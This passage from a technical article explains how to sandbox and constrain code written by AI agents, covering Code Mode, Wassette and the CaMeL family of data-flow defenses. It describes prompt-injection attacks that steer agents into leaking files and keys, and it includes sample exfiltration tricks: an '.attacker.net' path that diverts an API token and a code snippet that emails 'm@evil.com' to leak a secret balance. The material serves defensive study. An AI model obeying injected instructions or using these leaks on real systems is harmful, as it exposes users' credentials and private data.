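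When the operating system can't enforce the sandbox's rules, Codex on a Mac refuses to run the command, while Zed on Linux may run it without the sandbox and show a warning. A programmer at the keyboard can react to a warning, but nobody will see it if a saved tool runs at night, so refusal is the better choice for saved tools.

In Codex, as in Claude Code, the profile does not control MCP servers. But Codex has a command that runs any program under a chosen profile, and Bolin's article includes an example that sandboxes an MCP server. A user can put a saved tool back inside the sandbox this way.

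### Running the agent inside or outside

If the whole agent runs in the sandbox, the same limits apply to its file tools, its hooks and every tool it makes, so no one has to confine each part separately. NVIDIA recommends this broad coverage. But the sandbox must then also contain everything the agent needs, including its login for the language model. OpenAI warns that if Codex runs in a development container with its own sandbox turned off, a malicious project can send out anything in the container, including Codex's credentials.

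Willison chose to run the agent outside the sandbox, rather than inside it, and have it send in only its commands. This prevents the agent from changing its own program or immediate surroundings, and makes the boundary easier for people to check. Willison's team released three prototypes in November 2026: the WebAssembly emulator, one based on Apple's containers and one based on QEMU, a program that runs virtual machines. All three accept the same kinds of request, so Claude Code, Codex or a smaller agent called Pi can use any of them. Data can leave the sandbox only through the folders the user has mounted and the proxy.

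A sandbox is effective only if the agent can't also act outside it. When Willison starts Pi with the sandbox, he includes an option that turns off Pi's built-in tools. Without that option, Pi could still read files on the real disk, bypassing the sandbox around its commands.

If only an agent's commands run inside the sandbox, the host can keep the library of saved tools and the record of each tool's permissions outside it. A bad tool then can't rewrite another tool or give itself more access. This protection requires the host to keep the library out of the mounted folders or mount it read-only. Developers can also combine the two arrangements. OpenAI's sample development container includes bubblewrap, so Codex can confine each command a second time inside the container.

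### Keeping keys out of the sandbox

Many tools need a password or access key for a service. Putting the key in the sandbox is simplest, but then any code there can read it, copy it into a file or send it to an allowed domain.

Credential replacement avoids this. The tool sends its request without the key, or with a meaningless placeholder, and the proxy adds the real key only if the request is going to the service that the key belongs to. Willison's proxy works this way, and so do Docker's sandboxes, according to OSTechNix. The tutorial *Claude Code Sandboxing* describes a similar Claude Code setting called "mask", which gives the command a dummy value that the proxy exchanges for the real one.

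If a proxy adds the key to a tool's requests, a malicious tool can't steal the key and use it elsewhere. But the tool can still use the key while it runs, because the proxy adds it to harmful requests as well as useful ones. This is another confused deputy problem, with the proxy as the deputy. Anthropic lists broad credentials for an allowed domain as a separate risk for the same reason.

A proxy written for a specific service can also limit how a credential is used. In the web version of Claude Code, sandboxed code reaches GitHub through a proxy that can interpret version-control requests. Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* explains that the sandbox holds a specially made credential with limited rights. The proxy checks this credential and the content of the request, for instance that the code is going to the agreed branch, before attaching the real token. This protects the other branches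 as well as the token. The drawback is that someone has to write a proxy for each service, while plain replacement works for any service that takes a key.

OpenAI uses timing to similar effect in the cloud version of Codex. During setup, the environment can use the network and any secrets it needs to install software. Before the agent starts work, Codex removes the secrets and, by default, cuts off internet access. This works for keys needed only to download software, but not for a key that the tool needs every time it runs.

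### One sandbox for all tools, or one for each

The simplest way to run a library of tools is in a single sandbox with access to every folder and domain that any of them needs, but this gives each tool the others' access too. Suppose ten tools each use one private folder and one outside domain. In a shared sandbox, code from any tool can send data from any of the ten folders to any of the ten domains, which makes 100 possible routes. Giving each tool its own sandbox leaves only the ten routes that the tools were meant to have.

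Separate sandboxes also keep a bad run from affecting later ones. NVIDIA warns that long-lived sandboxes collect downloaded software, old scripts and stored passwords, which an attacker who gets in later can use. It suggests either destroying the sandbox after each task or rebuilding it on a schedule, such as weekly. Zed partly does this on Linux by clearing the temporary directory between commands. OpenSage does the opposite when it saves a container's contents for the next run, and its shared workspace connects tools that would otherwise be separate.

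Someone has to decide what each tool may access, which is hard when the tool could be any program. Wiesen rejected AppContainer, another Windows feature, for this reason. It offers a real boundary, but only for programs that "know, up front, exactly what they need to access", and Codex might run any program a developer uses. A saved agent-made tool is much closer to the kind of program AppContainer was made for. Its code no longer changes, the host can observe a few runs, and a person can turn those observations into a short list of allowed folders and domains. So it makes sense to use a general sandbox while the agent is writing and testing the tool, and a narrower one once the agent saves it.

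Splitting a single tool can help too. In the expense tool, only the part that reads receipts needs the folder, and only the part that fetches exchange rates needs the internet. If the host runs them separately and passes only a date and a three-letter currency code from the first to the second, a malicious library in the receipt reader has almost no way to get a receipt out. But the host has to check that the values are a date and a currency code, because otherwise the library could put a receipt's contents in the currency field.

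### An allowed domain can receive data

A list of allowed domains limits where a tool can connect, but not what it sends. Any request, even one meant to fetch something, can carry data in its address or body. If a tool can read a file and contact a server, it can send the file to that server.

The risk of data reaching an allowed domain depends on who can read it there. A small exchange-rate service might record a stolen receipt in its logs, but a stranger on the internet can't normally read those. Anthropic warns that allowing a broad domain such as github.com may let data out, because attackers can have accounts there too. The proxy would allow a request to the attacker's project as well as one to the user's, since both go to an allowed domain. OpenAI's *Permissions* states more generally that domain rules "do not determine whether an allowed destination is trustworthy".

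Read access and network access have to be set together. Letting a tool read the whole disk can be reasonable if it has no network access, because it can't send the data out itself. Letting it contact any site can also be reasonable if all it can read is something public, such as a price list. Problems arise when someone adds a domain to a sandbox whose read access was chosen with the network off. In Claude Code, for example, a user who allows github.com so that a tool can download a library also gives that tool a way to send out the keys in `~/.ssh`, unless the user has blocked that folder. Before adding a domain, it's worth checking whether anything the tool can read would do harm if it were sent there.

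Even when a sandbox blocks all network access, a generated tool can leak data through the agent. The tool's output goes back to the language model, and the agent may have other tools that can reach the internet. For example, a generated tool might print an access key along with a request to include it in a web address. If the agent follows the request, its web-fetching tool can send the key out. Claude Code's domain list does not apply to the web-fetching tool, so the only remaining protection is the permission rule for web fetching.

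### Files that take effect outside

A sandbox that lets an agent write to the working folder doesn't control how other programs later use the files there. For example, an agent may add a line to a Makefile, a file of build instructions. The line does nothing in the sandbox, but when the user next builds the project in an ordinary terminal, it runs with the user's full rights. Zed's documentation gives this example and another, in which an editor's helper programs execute code as soon as it appears in a project.

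Fadilpašić reported in July 2026 that researchers had found ways out of the sandboxes around leading coding agents (*Top AI coding agents can be easy victims to sandbox escapes*).

NVIDIA treats three limits as mandatory: no connections to arbitrary sites, no writing outside the workspace, and no changes to the agent's configuration files, wherever they are. It would not let users approve an agent's change to a configuration file, even once, and wants people to edit those files by hand. Files like the Makefile are harder to protect because editing them is often part of the agent's job. Zed's recommendation to review the changes before using them is good advice, but safety then depends again on a person noticing one bad line.

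The problem is more general for agent-made tools because a saved tool is a file that another program will run. If the agent writes and tests the tool in a sandbox but the host later runs it outside, the sandbox protects the host only during the test.

### The expense tool in a sandbox

Suppose the host gives the expense tool its own sandbox. The tool can read the receipts folder and write to an empty working folder, but it cannot see the rest of the disk. It can contact two domains, one for exchange rates and one for the team's online spreadsheet. The proxy adds the login for the spreadsheet.

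The sandbox limits much of the damage described earlier. When a hotel sends a tar file with a name full of `../` steps, the flawed extraction tool tries to write outside the working folder and the kernel blocks it. The tool can still overwrite files inside that folder, so the flaw remains, but the worker's documents and login scripts are safe. A library that searches the disk for access keys finds none. If the agent follows the stranger's instruction and adds a step that uploads every receipt to an unknown address, the proxy blocks the upload, and someone reading its log may notice that something is wrong.

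With Claude Code's default settings, the proxy would still block the upload, and the kernel would still stop the tar file from writing outside the working directory. But the tool could read the worker's keys and private letters and send them to the spreadsheet's domain. An attacker with access to any spreadsheet on the same service could try to make the tool write them there. Whether that works depends on what the login allows, because both spreadsheets are on the same domain.

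Even the strict sandbox doesn't stop mistakes in the tool's normal work. The tool can convert a month of receipts at the wrong rate, or replace the whole spreadsheet when it should have added a row. The proxy only checks that the request goes to the spreadsheet service. To allow new rows but forbid deletions, the worker needs a login with those limits or a proxy that can parse the service's requests, like the one for GitHub.

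When hotels start emailing their receipts, the tool can't retrieve them because it has no access to the login stored in the mail program, and the mail server is not on its list. The worker could add the mail server and have the proxy supply the password. The tool would never hold the password, but it could read the entire mailbox and, if the same login can send mail, write to strangers. A better solution is to have the mail program save attachments from the hotels into the receipts folder, so the tool can use them without any change to its permissions.

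## What changes when generated code can only call functions the host supplies?

In the third design, the program starts with no files, network connection or passwords, whereas a sandbox takes an ordinary program and removes some of its access. The program can get or change things outside itself only by calling functions that the host has passed in.

When generated code can only call functions the host supplies, the list of functions is also the list of permissions. This list can be more precise than a sandbox's rules, which name a folder or a domain, because a function can permit a single action, such as adding one row to one spreadsheet.

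### Starting with no access

WebAssembly programs can usually call only the outside functions their host supplies. They reach files and networks through a standard set of functions called WASI, whose documentation describes such code as having "no ambient authority". Ambient authority is the access an ordinary program gets just by running under someone's account, such as being able to open a file just by knowing its name.

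The alternative to ambient authority is a capability, an unforgeable reference that names a resource and grants the right to use it. If the host gives a program an object that stands for one folder, the program can use that folder, but it can't open another folder just by knowing its name. A function the host passes in works the same way.

The list of host-supplied functions limits the code only if the code can't break out of the sandbox it runs in.

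### One run of Code Mode

Cloudflare, which hosts websites and programs, introduced a system of this kind in September 2025. Varda and Pai argue in *Code Mode* that language models write code better than they make tool calls, because their training data contains millions of real programs but only a small number of contrived tool calls.

Cloudflare's *Codemode* has an example with two tools, one that looks up the weather and one that sends email. A run goes like this:

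1. The host collects the tools' definitions, which list each tool's inputs. For an MCP server, it fetches them from the server.
2. Code Mode turns each definition into a typed function in TypeScript, a form of JavaScript that records what kind of value each input should be. The tool's description becomes a comment.
3. The model sees these functions and a single tool, which runs code. It writes a short program that gets the weather in London and, if the answer contains the word "sunny", emails the team.
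4. The host starts an isolate, a small separate JavaScript environment, and loads the program. The usual commands for opening a network connection fail there.
5. When the program asks for the weather, a stand-in object catches the call and sends the function's name and inputs to the host.
6. The host runs the real tool. If the tool needs an access key, the host adds it to the outgoing request, then passes the answer back to the program.
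7. The program finishes, and the model gets its result and anything it printed.

An isolate starts in a few milliseconds and needs only a few megabytes of memory, so Cloudflare creates a new one for every program and then throws it away. That avoids the old files and passwords that collect in long-lived sandboxes.

The types in step 2 help the model write correct calls, but they are not a security check, because the program can still pass something else. According to Cloudflare's *Code Mode API reference*, the main package "does not validate inputs against schemas", although a version for one popular toolkit does so when it can. A function that expects an order number therefore has to check that it received one.

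### Functions compared with a filtered network

Varda and Pai prefer functions to a proxy with a list of allowed addresses. With a proxy, the person setting the rules has trouble working out which traffic a service needs, and the model has to write code without being told which requests will be blocked. A function makes clear to both what is allowed. This is a good argument when a suitable function exists, but otherwise someone has to write one, whereas a proxy only needs another domain on its list.

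Generated code can't leak the keys that the host adds to requests, because those keys stay with the host. Varda and Pai go further and write that the AI "cannot possibly write code that leaks any keys", which is too strong because a program can receive keys in other ways. For example, if a service creates a new access key and returns it in its reply, the program has that key. Cloudflare's *Build a Code Mode MCP server*, a guide from November 2026, tells developers to keep secrets out of tool results and API descriptions because the program can read both.

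A developer can also weaken the design through the settings. Cloudflare blocks the isolate's network access by default, but one option routes its traffic through a service the developer chooses, and another adds resources to the isolate. Anyone reviewing a Code Mode system should check these options as well as the functions.

### A fixed list or one general request

The first of two patterns in Cloudflare's guide wraps an existing MCP server and gives the program one typed function for each of the server's tools. If the server has a tool for looking up an order but none for canceling one, the program can't cancel an order.

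The second pattern is for services too large to describe this way. Cloudflare's API, which other programs use to control its products, has more than 2,500 operations. *Code Mode* (Carey, February 2026) describes a server that covers all of them with two tools. The agent uses `search` to run code over the API's description and find the operations it needs. It uses `execute` to run code that can call any of them through a general request function.

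In Carey's example, a user asks an agent to protect a website from attacks that flood it with traffic. The agent's search returns ten operations on firewall settings, four that only read them and six that create or change them. The agent then checks the details of one operation, lists the existing rules and fetches two sets of them to inspect, using four tool calls in all. The request function it uses to read the firewall rules could also rewrite them.

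The host's developer writes the code that limits what the function can do. In Cloudflare's guide, the generated program chooses a path and a method, which can be GET (read), POST, PUT or PATCH (create or change), or DELETE. The sample host code checks that the path starts with a slash, attaches the user's access token and sends the request. It doesn't check the method, so `DELETE /orders/123` goes through if the token allows it.

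The check for a leading slash matters because the host joins the path directly to the service's address, `https://api.example.com`. Without the check, a program could supply the path `.attacker.net/x`, and the request would go to `api.example.com.attacker.net`, a machine that an attacker could own, with the user's token attached. A shorter sample in *Codemode* joins the address and path without checking for the slash.

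Developers can combine the patterns by accident. A Cloudflare component reads an API's description and creates a typed function for each operation, but it always supplies the general request function as well. A developer who guards the typed function for deleting an order also has to guard the general one.

### Writing a narrower function

The host can narrow access by taking choices away from the program. In this pseudocode, `send` is the host's own function for contacting the service:

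```
# General: the program chooses the method and the path
function request(method, path, body):
    require path starts with "/"
    return send(method, path, body, token)

# Read-only: the program chooses the path
function read(path):
    require path starts with "/"
    return send("GET", path, nothing, token)

# One customer: the program chooses the month
function invoices_for(customer):
    function list_invoices(month):
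        require month has the form "2026-11"
        return send("GET",
            "/customers/" + customer + "/invoices?month=" + month,
            nothing, token)
    return list_invoices
```

The read-only function can't delete an order as long as the service follows the convention that GET requests don't change anything. It can still read every customer's records, and it blocks some harmless requests because some services use POST for complicated searches.

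The host creates the third function by calling `invoices_for(17)` before the program starts, and passes in only the result. The program can use this function to request November's invoices, but it can't choose another customer because the function doesn't take a customer number. The program holds a capability for customer 17's invoices, even though the host's token may cover every customer.

Checking that the path begins with `/customers/17/` isn't enough to restrict the general function to customer 17, because a program can ask for `/customers/17/../18/invoices`. The two dots work as they did in the tar file, so the request reaches customer 18. The host has to work out the final path before checking it or, better, build the path itself.

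### Anthropic's version with tools as files

In November 2025, Anthropic described a similar design in which each tool appears to the agent as a code file. Each MCP server, such as the one for Google Drive or the customer database Salesforce, has its own folder. The agent lists the folders, opens the files for the tools it needs and writes a program that calls those tools.

Suppose a user wants a meeting transcript copied from Google Drive into a customer's record in Salesforce. With ordinary tool calls, the model reads the transcript and then writes it out again for the second tool. Anthropic estimates this could add 50,000 tokens (the pieces of text a model reads and writes) for a two-hour meeting. A program can instead hold the transcript in a variable and pass it on without the model seeing it. A program can also filter a spreadsheet of 10,000 rows and show the model only five.

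This also protects the model from instructions hidden in the text, as long as the program doesn't print it.

To protect personal data, Anthropic also suggests that the program connecting the agent to its tools replace names, email addresses and phone numbers with placeholders before the model sees them. The program keeps a table of the real values and restores them when the agent's code passes a placeholder to another tool. The model can then move contact details from a spreadsheet to Salesforce without being able to repeat them in its answer. The connecting program also has to control which tools may receive the real values, because otherwise it would restore them in an email to a stranger too.

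In Anthropic's version, unlike Cloudflare's, programs can save files between steps. Anthropic cautions that running agent-written code requires a secure environment with a sandbox, resource limits and monitoring, which direct tool calls don't need.

### Why developers adopted it

The main attraction of this design was that it uses fewer tokens. An agent with many tools ordinarily has to read all their definitions before it starts work, which is slow and expensive and leaves less room for the task. In Anthropic's example, loading only the definitions the agent needs cuts token use from 150,000 to 2,000. Carey calculates that an ordinary MCP server for the whole Cloudflare API would use 1.17 million tokens, more than the most advanced models could read at once, while the server with two tools uses about 1,000.

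These figures are a good reason to use the design, but they measure text length, not security. The bigger saving comes from the looser pattern, in which a single function reaches everything. Developers can keep most of that saving without a general request function. In the version that Cloudflare's *How Code Mode works* described in June 2026, a program can search a long list of typed functions and read the definitions of only those it needs.

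Carey lists versions of this approach outside Cloudflare, in the agent Goose and Anthropic's software kit. Cloudflare says companies that connect their staff to MCP servers through it can make Code Mode unavailable, optional, on by default or compulsory, and that new setups start with it optional. As of June 2026, Cloudflare still called its Code Mode package experimental.

### WebAssembly tools that declare their permissions

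Code Mode gives a program the functions the developer has connected. In Wassette, which Microsoft released in August 2025, each tool instead comes with its own list of permissions. The tools are WebAssembly components, packaged programs with defined inputs and outputs, which an agent can fetch from an online registry and run. According to Microsoft's *Introducing Wassette* (2025), a component has no access by default, and its publisher can sign it so that others can verify where it came from.

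According to Microsoft's *Frequently Asked Questions (FAQ)*, a component must declare which resources it needs. The example policy in Microsoft's *What is Wassette?* lets a tool read and write in a workspace folder, read one settings file and contact one web address. A reviewer can read such a list in seconds without looking at the code.

These rules limit which folders and addresses a component can reach, but not what it does there. A component that may contact a spreadsheet service can send it any request, so it can delete rows as well as add them. To allow one without the other, someone still has to write a narrower function. A signature shows who published a tool and that nobody has changed it since, but not whether the tool is safe.

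Wassette also gives the agent built-in tools for managing components and their permissions. If an injected instruction can cause the agent to widen a component's permissions, the declared list offers no protection, so the host should require a person to approve any call that does this.

Wassette is still at an early stage. Its latest release as of June 2026 was version 0.4.0, from February 4, according to GitPedia's *Wassette*. The project's introduction, as copied in MCP Directory's *wassette*, describes it as "not production ready yet". Developers also have to rewrite existing MCP servers as components to use them with Wassette. An agent could write a new tool as a component from the start, so this work matters less for agent-made tools than for existing ones.

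### Permitted calls can still do harm together

Cloudflare's November 2026 guide states, "Code execution does not replace authorization." The isolate guarantees that a program acts only through the supplied functions. The host must still decide, inside each function and before anything changes, whether the call should happen for this user and with these inputs.

Code Mode hides individual calls from the program that connects to the server. With ordinary tools, that program receives each call by name and can ask the user for approval before sending an email. In Code Mode, it receives only one call to a tool named `code`, which may contain a hundred actions. The model doesn't receive the intermediate results either, so it can't check one for errors before the generated code moves on to the next step.

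The built-in limits also don't prevent much harm. Programs stop after 60 seconds by default, but a loop can change many records in that time. Cloudflare also cuts results to about 6,000 tokens before they reach the model, but this doesn't limit what the program does. A program that has emptied a database may return only the word "done". A limit on how many times a program may call each function would be more useful.

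Functions that are harmless separately can be dangerous together. A program that can call one function to read customer records and another to send email can mail the records to anyone. Varda and Pai's example of a converted MCP server shows how easily this can happen. It has four functions for reading and searching a software project's documentation and code, one of which fetches content from any web address. The isolate has no internet access, but a program can get around this by putting data in a web address and calling that function to fetch it.

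The host can prevent this by leaving out the fetching function or restricting it to a few sites. If a task needs both customer records and email, the host has to determine whether the text in the email came from the records. Ordinary host functions can't determine this, because each one receives only its own inputs.

The host at least gets a useful record. In Cloudflare's newer version, every call to an outside service passes through a component that logs the function and its inputs and can hold the call until someone approves it. This log shows which row a program added to a spreadsheet, while an ordinary sandbox's log might show only that the program contacted the spreadsheet service.

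The same record helps reverse mistakes. A developer can write an undo step for a function, and the host can then undo a bad program's calls, starting with the last. But the effects of functions without an undo step remain, and nobody can take back an email that someone has read.

### Who has to act to add a data source

Under the first two designs, an agent can often get to new data by itself, or with one more entry in a settings file. Here the answer depends on which functions the host supplies:

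| What the host supplies | What the program can do | Who adds a new data source |
|---|---|---|
| One function per tool | The listed actions | A developer, by connecting another server or writing a function |
| A general request function | Anything the access token allows | Nobody, if the token covers it; otherwise the user, by granting more |
| A function fixed to one customer or folder | One kind of action on one resource | A developer, by writing a function |
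| A WebAssembly component with a policy | Anything involving the listed folders and addresses | Whoever controls the policy |

The general request function has by far the widest reach within one service. Carey writes that when Cloudflare adds a product, the same two tools can find and use it without new definitions. This is convenient for unplanned work, but a tool's reach can then grow without anyone reviewing the tool.

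Most of the limits then come from the token's permissions. With Carey's server, the user chooses these when connecting. A later update, described in Cloudflare's changelog, lets the user start with minimal access. If a call needs a permission the token lacks, the server identifies it and the user's program asks whether to grant it. This is a good compromise, because the request comes when the user knows what the task is. But the token keeps each new permission afterward, so permissions accumulate unless someone removes them.

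### The expense tool with host functions

For the expense tool, the host could supply four functions: one lists the receipts, one reads a receipt, one returns the exchange rate for a currency and date, and one adds a row to the team's spreadsheet. The agent writes the code that connects them.

The tool can't delete a receipt or overwrite a colleague's expenses, because the host supplies no function that does either. If a hotel sends a tar file containing a file name full of `../` steps, the program can unpack it in memory, but it has no disk to write to. If the agent follows the stranger's instruction to upload every receipt, the code it writes has nowhere to send them. The exchange-rate function accepts only a date and a currency from a fixed list, so it's of little use for leaking text.

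Leaks through the spreadsheet function are harder to prevent. It needs a date, an amount and a currency, which the host can check, but the worker probably also wants a description. A program could put the text of a private receipt there for the whole team to read. The host can limit the description to a short list of categories, such as "hotel" and "train". A malicious program could still hide text in the amounts across many rows, which is one reason to limit the number of rows it can add per run.

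When hotels start emailing their receipts, the tool can't read them until someone gives it a function that can. The quickest fix is to connect an MCP server for the mailbox, but that may add functions for reading every message and sending new ones. A developer could instead write one function that returns only attachments sent from a list of hotel addresses. Senders can forge their addresses, so some attachments may be malicious, but the tool still can't access the rest of the mailbox.

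The tool can still convert a month of receipts at the wrong rate, because the agent wrote the calculation and each row the tool adds looks valid. A developer could move the conversion into a host function, so that all the tools that need it share one tested version. This would reduce the amount of code the agent could get wrong, but the developer would have to write more.

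## Can generated code be checked for where data goes?

If a program is allowed to read customer records and send email, host functions can't stop it from emailing the records. Sandboxes have the same gap. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of an agent that is allowed to read a private file and call a cloud language model. If the agent sends the file to that model, the sandbox allows both steps, and the leak "never crosses a sandbox boundary".

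The fourth design adds data-flow rules to prevent such leaks. The agent still writes code, but the host tracks how data moves through it, either by labeling the data while the code runs or by analyzing the code beforehand. Labels can reflect facts available only during the run, such as who can open a shared file that day. Analysis lets the host reject a bad program before it sends or changes anything.

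### How CaMeL labels data

Google DeepMind introduced CaMeL, a leading system that uses labels, in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025). CaMeL has two language models and an interpreter, a program that runs code step by step. One model, the planner, receives only the user's request and writes a program from it in a restricted form of Python. The other model, the reader, processes untrusted text such as emails and web pages, but has no tools. The interpreter runs the planner's program, calling tools and passing text to the reader as the program specifies.

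Suppose a user wants to tell Bob about a meeting, and Bob's address is somewhere in a chat channel. In an example adapted from Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*, the planner writes a program like this:

```
messages = read_channel("general")
address = ask_reader("What is Bob's email address?", messages)
send_message(address, "Meeting at 3pm")
```

An attacker has posted a message in the channel telling agents to send out the user's files. The planner never sees this message, so the program keeps the same three steps. The reader sees it and may follow it, but can only return an answer. The attacker can still make it return the attacker's address, and the program then sends the message about the meeting there. As *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026) points out, separating the two models protects the sequence of actions but doesn't necessarily protect the data in them.

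CaMeL protects the data by giving every value two labels. "Sources" records where the value came from, and "Readers" records who may see it. For a calendar event, the readers might be the user and the invitees. The event's description is trusted only if the user wrote it. When a program computes a value from other values, the result inherits their labels, so an address taken from the channel still counts as coming from the channel.

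Before each tool call, the interpreter runs a policy, a function that receives the tool's name, its inputs and their labels, and allows or denies the call. In pseudocode, a policy for sending messages could be:

```
function may_send(recipient, text):
    if recipient has an untrusted source: deny
    if recipient is not among the readers of text: deny
    allow
```

Checking where the recipient's address came from blocks an address supplied by the attacker. A separate check on who may read the data keeps customer records out of an email to a stranger, even if the user typed in the stranger's address.

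This policy also blocks Bob's real address, because it came from the same channel as the attacker's. A label records only where a value came from, not whether it is correct. To send Bob the message, the user could supply the address, or the planner could look it up in a source that the policy allows, such as the user's contacts.

### How well CaMeL works

The usual test is AgentDojo, a set of simulated office, banking, chat and travel tasks with attacks planted in the data that tools return. In CaMeL's published results, as reproduced by Odersky and colleagues, one of about 950 attacks succeeded with OpenAI's o4-mini-high, and the agent finished the user's task in roughly three-quarters of the runs. With Gemini 2.5 Pro, no attack succeeded, but the agent finished fewer than half of the tasks, in part because it completed almost none of the travel tasks.

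Other researchers have measured the same strong protection but a larger drop in completed tasks. *SecureClaw* (2026), which presents a competing defense, adapted CaMeL's released code and ran it on all of AgentDojo. None of the 629 attacks succeeded, but CaMeL completed only 29 of the 97 tasks that contained no attack, compared with 59 for SecureClaw.

Much of CaMeL's loss in task completion comes from its policies. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, ran AgentDojo's 16 banking tasks three times each. Turning on CaMeL's policies reduced the number of completed runs from 32 of 48 to 18 with GPT-5.2, and from 34 to 18 with MiMo-v2.5. Sixteen tasks are too few for a precise estimate, but the drop is large and appeared with both models.

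Garby and colleagues also checked how often a policy is needed to stop an attack. In 97 of the 144 pairings of a banking task with an attack, the user's task gives the planner no reason to call the tool the attacker needs. For example, a program that summarizes recent payments contains no step that sends money. In these pairings, keeping the planner away from untrusted text is nearly always enough to stop the attack. Even in the other 47, almost every attack failed with the policies off, and every one failed with them on. On this benchmark, the policies stopped only a handful of extra attacks and cut the number of completed tasks by about half. They matter more against an attacker who targets the data in a step the plan already contains.

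Policies also block legitimate tasks. When Nikolaou and colleagues ran AgentDojo's 97 tasks without attacks, using Claude Haiku 4.5, both CaMeL and their extension of it blocked 17 of them. This isn't simply a fault in the policies. If a user asks an agent to pay whatever bill is in a file, the account number has to come from the file, so a rule against untrusted account numbers forbids the payment.

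### Planning before seeing any data

*Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) describes a drawback of CaMeL that remains even without policies. An ordinary agent calls a tool, looks at the result and then decides how to use it. CaMeL's planner has to write the code that processes a result before any result exists, so it needs to know each tool's output format. AgentDojo's tool descriptions don't include the format, so the researchers added it, as CaMeL's developers had done.

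Each tool's output format only has to be declared once, which should be easy for agent-made tools because the agent can do it when it writes the tool. It is harder when a tool returns arbitrary text written by a stranger. The planner can ask the reader to extract particular fields from that text, but it has to know which fields to ask for. It also has to foresee every action the task might need, because untrusted data can affect which of the program's existing branches runs but can't add a new one.

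Peters-Gill and colleagues measured this loss by running CaMeL with no policies on AssetOpsBench, a set of industrial maintenance tasks that a coordinating agent divides among four others. CaMeL reduced the completion rate by an average of 21.6 percentage points across five models. For the two strongest, Claude Fable 5 and GPT-5.5, the average reduction was 13.4 points. Better planners therefore seem to lose less, but even they can't complete a task that requires a data flow the policies forbid.

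Someone also has to write and maintain a policy for every sensitive tool. Tallam and Miller (2025) warn in *Operationalizing CaMeL* that in a company with hundreds of tools, these policies will duplicate and contradict one another. An agent that keeps making tools adds to this work, unless the host gives each new tool a strict default policy.

### Where the labels get lost

A label protects data only if it stays attached to it, and Garby and colleagues found several places where CaMeL's interpreter drops the label. In the simplest case, a program inserts an untrusted value into fixed text, and the interpreter treats the result as trusted.

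A subtler leak goes through code that doesn't run. This program is a simplified version of their example:

```
low = True
if balance > 10000:
    low = False
if low:
    send_email("m@evil.com", "hello")
```

The balance is secret. If it is 8,000, the program skips the line that changes `low`, so the interpreter never marks `low` as secret, although its value depends on the balance. The program then sends the email, which contains nothing private, but the attacker can infer from its arrival that the balance is at most 10,000. Repeating the test with other limits would reveal the exact amount. An attacker can't easily put such code into CaMeL, because the planner doesn't read untrusted text. The risk is greater with an agent-made tool if the agent read a stranger's web page or copied someone's code while writing it.

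CaMeL's retry loop leaks information in a similar way. When a program fails, ordinary code outside the interpreter prompts the planner to write another. A secret can affect whether a policy blocked the last program, so each retry can reveal a little more about that secret.

Labels can also disappear when text enters a conversation. Odersky and colleagues note that once a model has read a labeled value, nothing connects its later words to the label. Labels can also be lost between agents. Peters-Gill and colleagues built a system in which a coordinating agent asked a database agent for information about job applicants and passed a summary to a notification agent to send to a colleague. Each agent ran CaMeL separately. An attacker had planted an instruction in the database to email the data to an outside address. The first two agents kept the instruction away from their planners, but the notification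 agent received it as part of its own request, which the agent treated as trusted, and sent the email.

The fix is to send instructions and data separately. The receiving planner sees an instruction such as "send the provided content", while the content travels in a variable with its labels. In a version of AgentDojo with several agents, the average attack success rate was 12.9% without CaMeL, 0.2% with CaMeL in each agent and 0.0% with the fix. Without CaMeL, the attacks succeeded in 36.1% of runs with GPT-4.1 but in none with GPT-5.5, so they are too weak to show how much CaMeL protects the newest models.

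Garby and colleagues responded to the leaks by designing a small programming language, LLMbda, and using the proof checker Lean to prove that it satisfies a form of noninterference. If two runs differ only in a secret, an outsider must see the same range of results with the same probabilities, except that one run may fail to finish. The proof covers the same program that calls the language model, so there is no separate, unchecked version.

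An agent built in LLMbda completed 36 of the 48 banking runs with GPT-5.2 and stopped all but two of 1,296 attacks across three models. It did better than CaMeL partly because its planner can declare in advance that it accepts particular untrusted data for a certain purpose. The agent also enforces only some of CaMeL's policies. The comparison shows that a system with proofs can still get work done, but because of these differences it doesn't show that proofs make an agent more useful.

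### Rejecting a plan before it starts

CaMeL may not detect a forbidden call until the tenth step, after the first nine have already changed something. Nikolaou and colleagues' CaMeLoT checks the whole program before it runs. It maps every path the run could take, then uses a model checker, a program that searches such maps, to look for a path that breaks a rule.

For the message to Bob, the rule requires every call to `send_message` to have a trusted recipient. The checker finds a path on which the address comes from the reader and returns that path as a counterexample. The planner can use it to repair the program before any tool runs.

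Rules of this kind can also cover the order of actions. Nikolaou and colleagues tested an agent that handles security alerts. One rule required it to get a person's approval before cutting a computer off from the network, and another required it to resolve or escalate every ticket it opened. The checker caught all seven plans the researchers had deliberately made unsafe, while a simplified CaMeL caught one. The researchers chose these rules because CaMeL can't easily express them, so the result shows what the checker adds but doesn't measure how often agents make such mistakes.

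The checker could fully reproduce 22 of the 28 CaMeL policies the researchers tried. The other six depend at least partly on facts that don't exist until the program runs, such as who has access to a file at that moment. The checker treats uncertain data as untrusted and allows for loops running any number of times. It therefore rejects some safe programs but doesn't approve an unsafe one just because a fact is missing. CaMeL's own checks still run afterward.

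### TACIT and functions that can't leak

TACIT, Odersky and colleagues' system, relies mainly on the compiler, which checks code and prepares it to run. The agent writes its programs in Scala 3, where every value has a type, such as number or text. An experimental feature called capture checking also records in a value's type which capabilities that value can use.

A function that only turns one text into another has the type `String -> String`. If the function also writes to a file `f`, its type becomes `String ->{f} String`. Functions that use no capabilities are called pure. They can calculate, but they can't write to a file, contact a server or print.

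TACIT puts secrets in a container called `Classified`. The agent's code can't open the container, but it can pass a function to the container's `map` method, which applies the function to the secret inside. `map` accepts only pure functions and puts the result in a new `Classified` container. A program that tries to leak a key could look like this:

```
val key = readClassified("key.txt")
key.map(s => s.toUpperCase)          // accepted
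key.map(s => { f.write(s); s })      // rejected
```

The last line would write the key to an ordinary file. Because the function uses `f` and `map` doesn't allow that, the compiler rejects the whole program before any of it runs. It does this whether the agent wrote the line by mistake or because of an injected instruction.

If the agent prints a classified value, it sees only `Classified(****)`, while the user's terminal shows the real text. The main agent can also work with secret documents without reading them. To get a summary, for example, the program can pass a document to a separate trusted model that has no tools, and the summary also comes back in a container.

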